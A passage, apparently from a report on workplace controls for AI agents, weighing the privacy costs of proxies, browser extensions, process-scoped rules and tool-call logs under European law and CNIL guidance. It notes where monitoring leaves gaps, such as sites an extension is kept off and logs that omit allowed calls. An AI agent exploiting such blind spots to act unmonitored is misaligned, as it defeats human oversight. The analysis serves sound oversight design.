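Agents can expose many more people in this position. In the running example, the shared document may contain comments from colleagues. Another task might involve a customer database or a mailbox with years of messages. The developer cannot consent for all these people, and the company cannot realistically ask everyone who might write to its staff. In Europe, the company needs a legal basis that does not depend on their consent, and they have the same rights over their data as employees do. CNIL says an employer must also inform visitors and outside consultants when they use its monitored network.

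The best protection for people whose data might be intercepted is to collect less. A control can reach deep into the system and still cover few people, as Argus and ActPlane do by limiting their rules to the agent's own processes. A proxy can decrypt traffic from only the agent's virtual machine or user account, leaving the developer's own browsing alone. A browser extension with access to all websites has less privilege than either, but it can read the developer's private messages even when no agent is running.

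Administrators can reduce this exposure with a Chrome policy that keeps an extension off chosen sites, such as banks and private webmail. However, an agent could do serious harm on those sites, and the extension could no longer stop it. It is better to bar the agent from those sites as well, so that only the person can use them, without monitoring.

### Personal data in tool-call logs

Supporters of controls at the protocol boundary might argue that these controls need no consent because they read only what the agent sends and receives. This is nearly true for the device, where only the agent's configuration changes.

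The logs can still contain personal data. The `share_document` call in the running example includes the recipient's email address. The calls that Li and colleagues describe contain recipients, attachments and file paths, and a path often includes the user's name. Results can reveal more, since a mailbox search may return messages from dozens of people. In Europe, an employer that stores this information needs a legal basis and has to inform its staff, as it would if the same text came from decrypted traffic.

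Such a control is easier to justify, however, because it records nothing while the developer browses without the agent. It can also check an argument without storing it, but if the argument isn't stored, an investigator may be unable to find out who received a shared document.

A company could compromise by storing full arguments only for calls the proxy refuses, much as CNIL would let a web proxy keep a request's content only when the proxy detects malicious code. But if a rule mistakenly allowed the agent to share the document, the log would lack the recipient's address.
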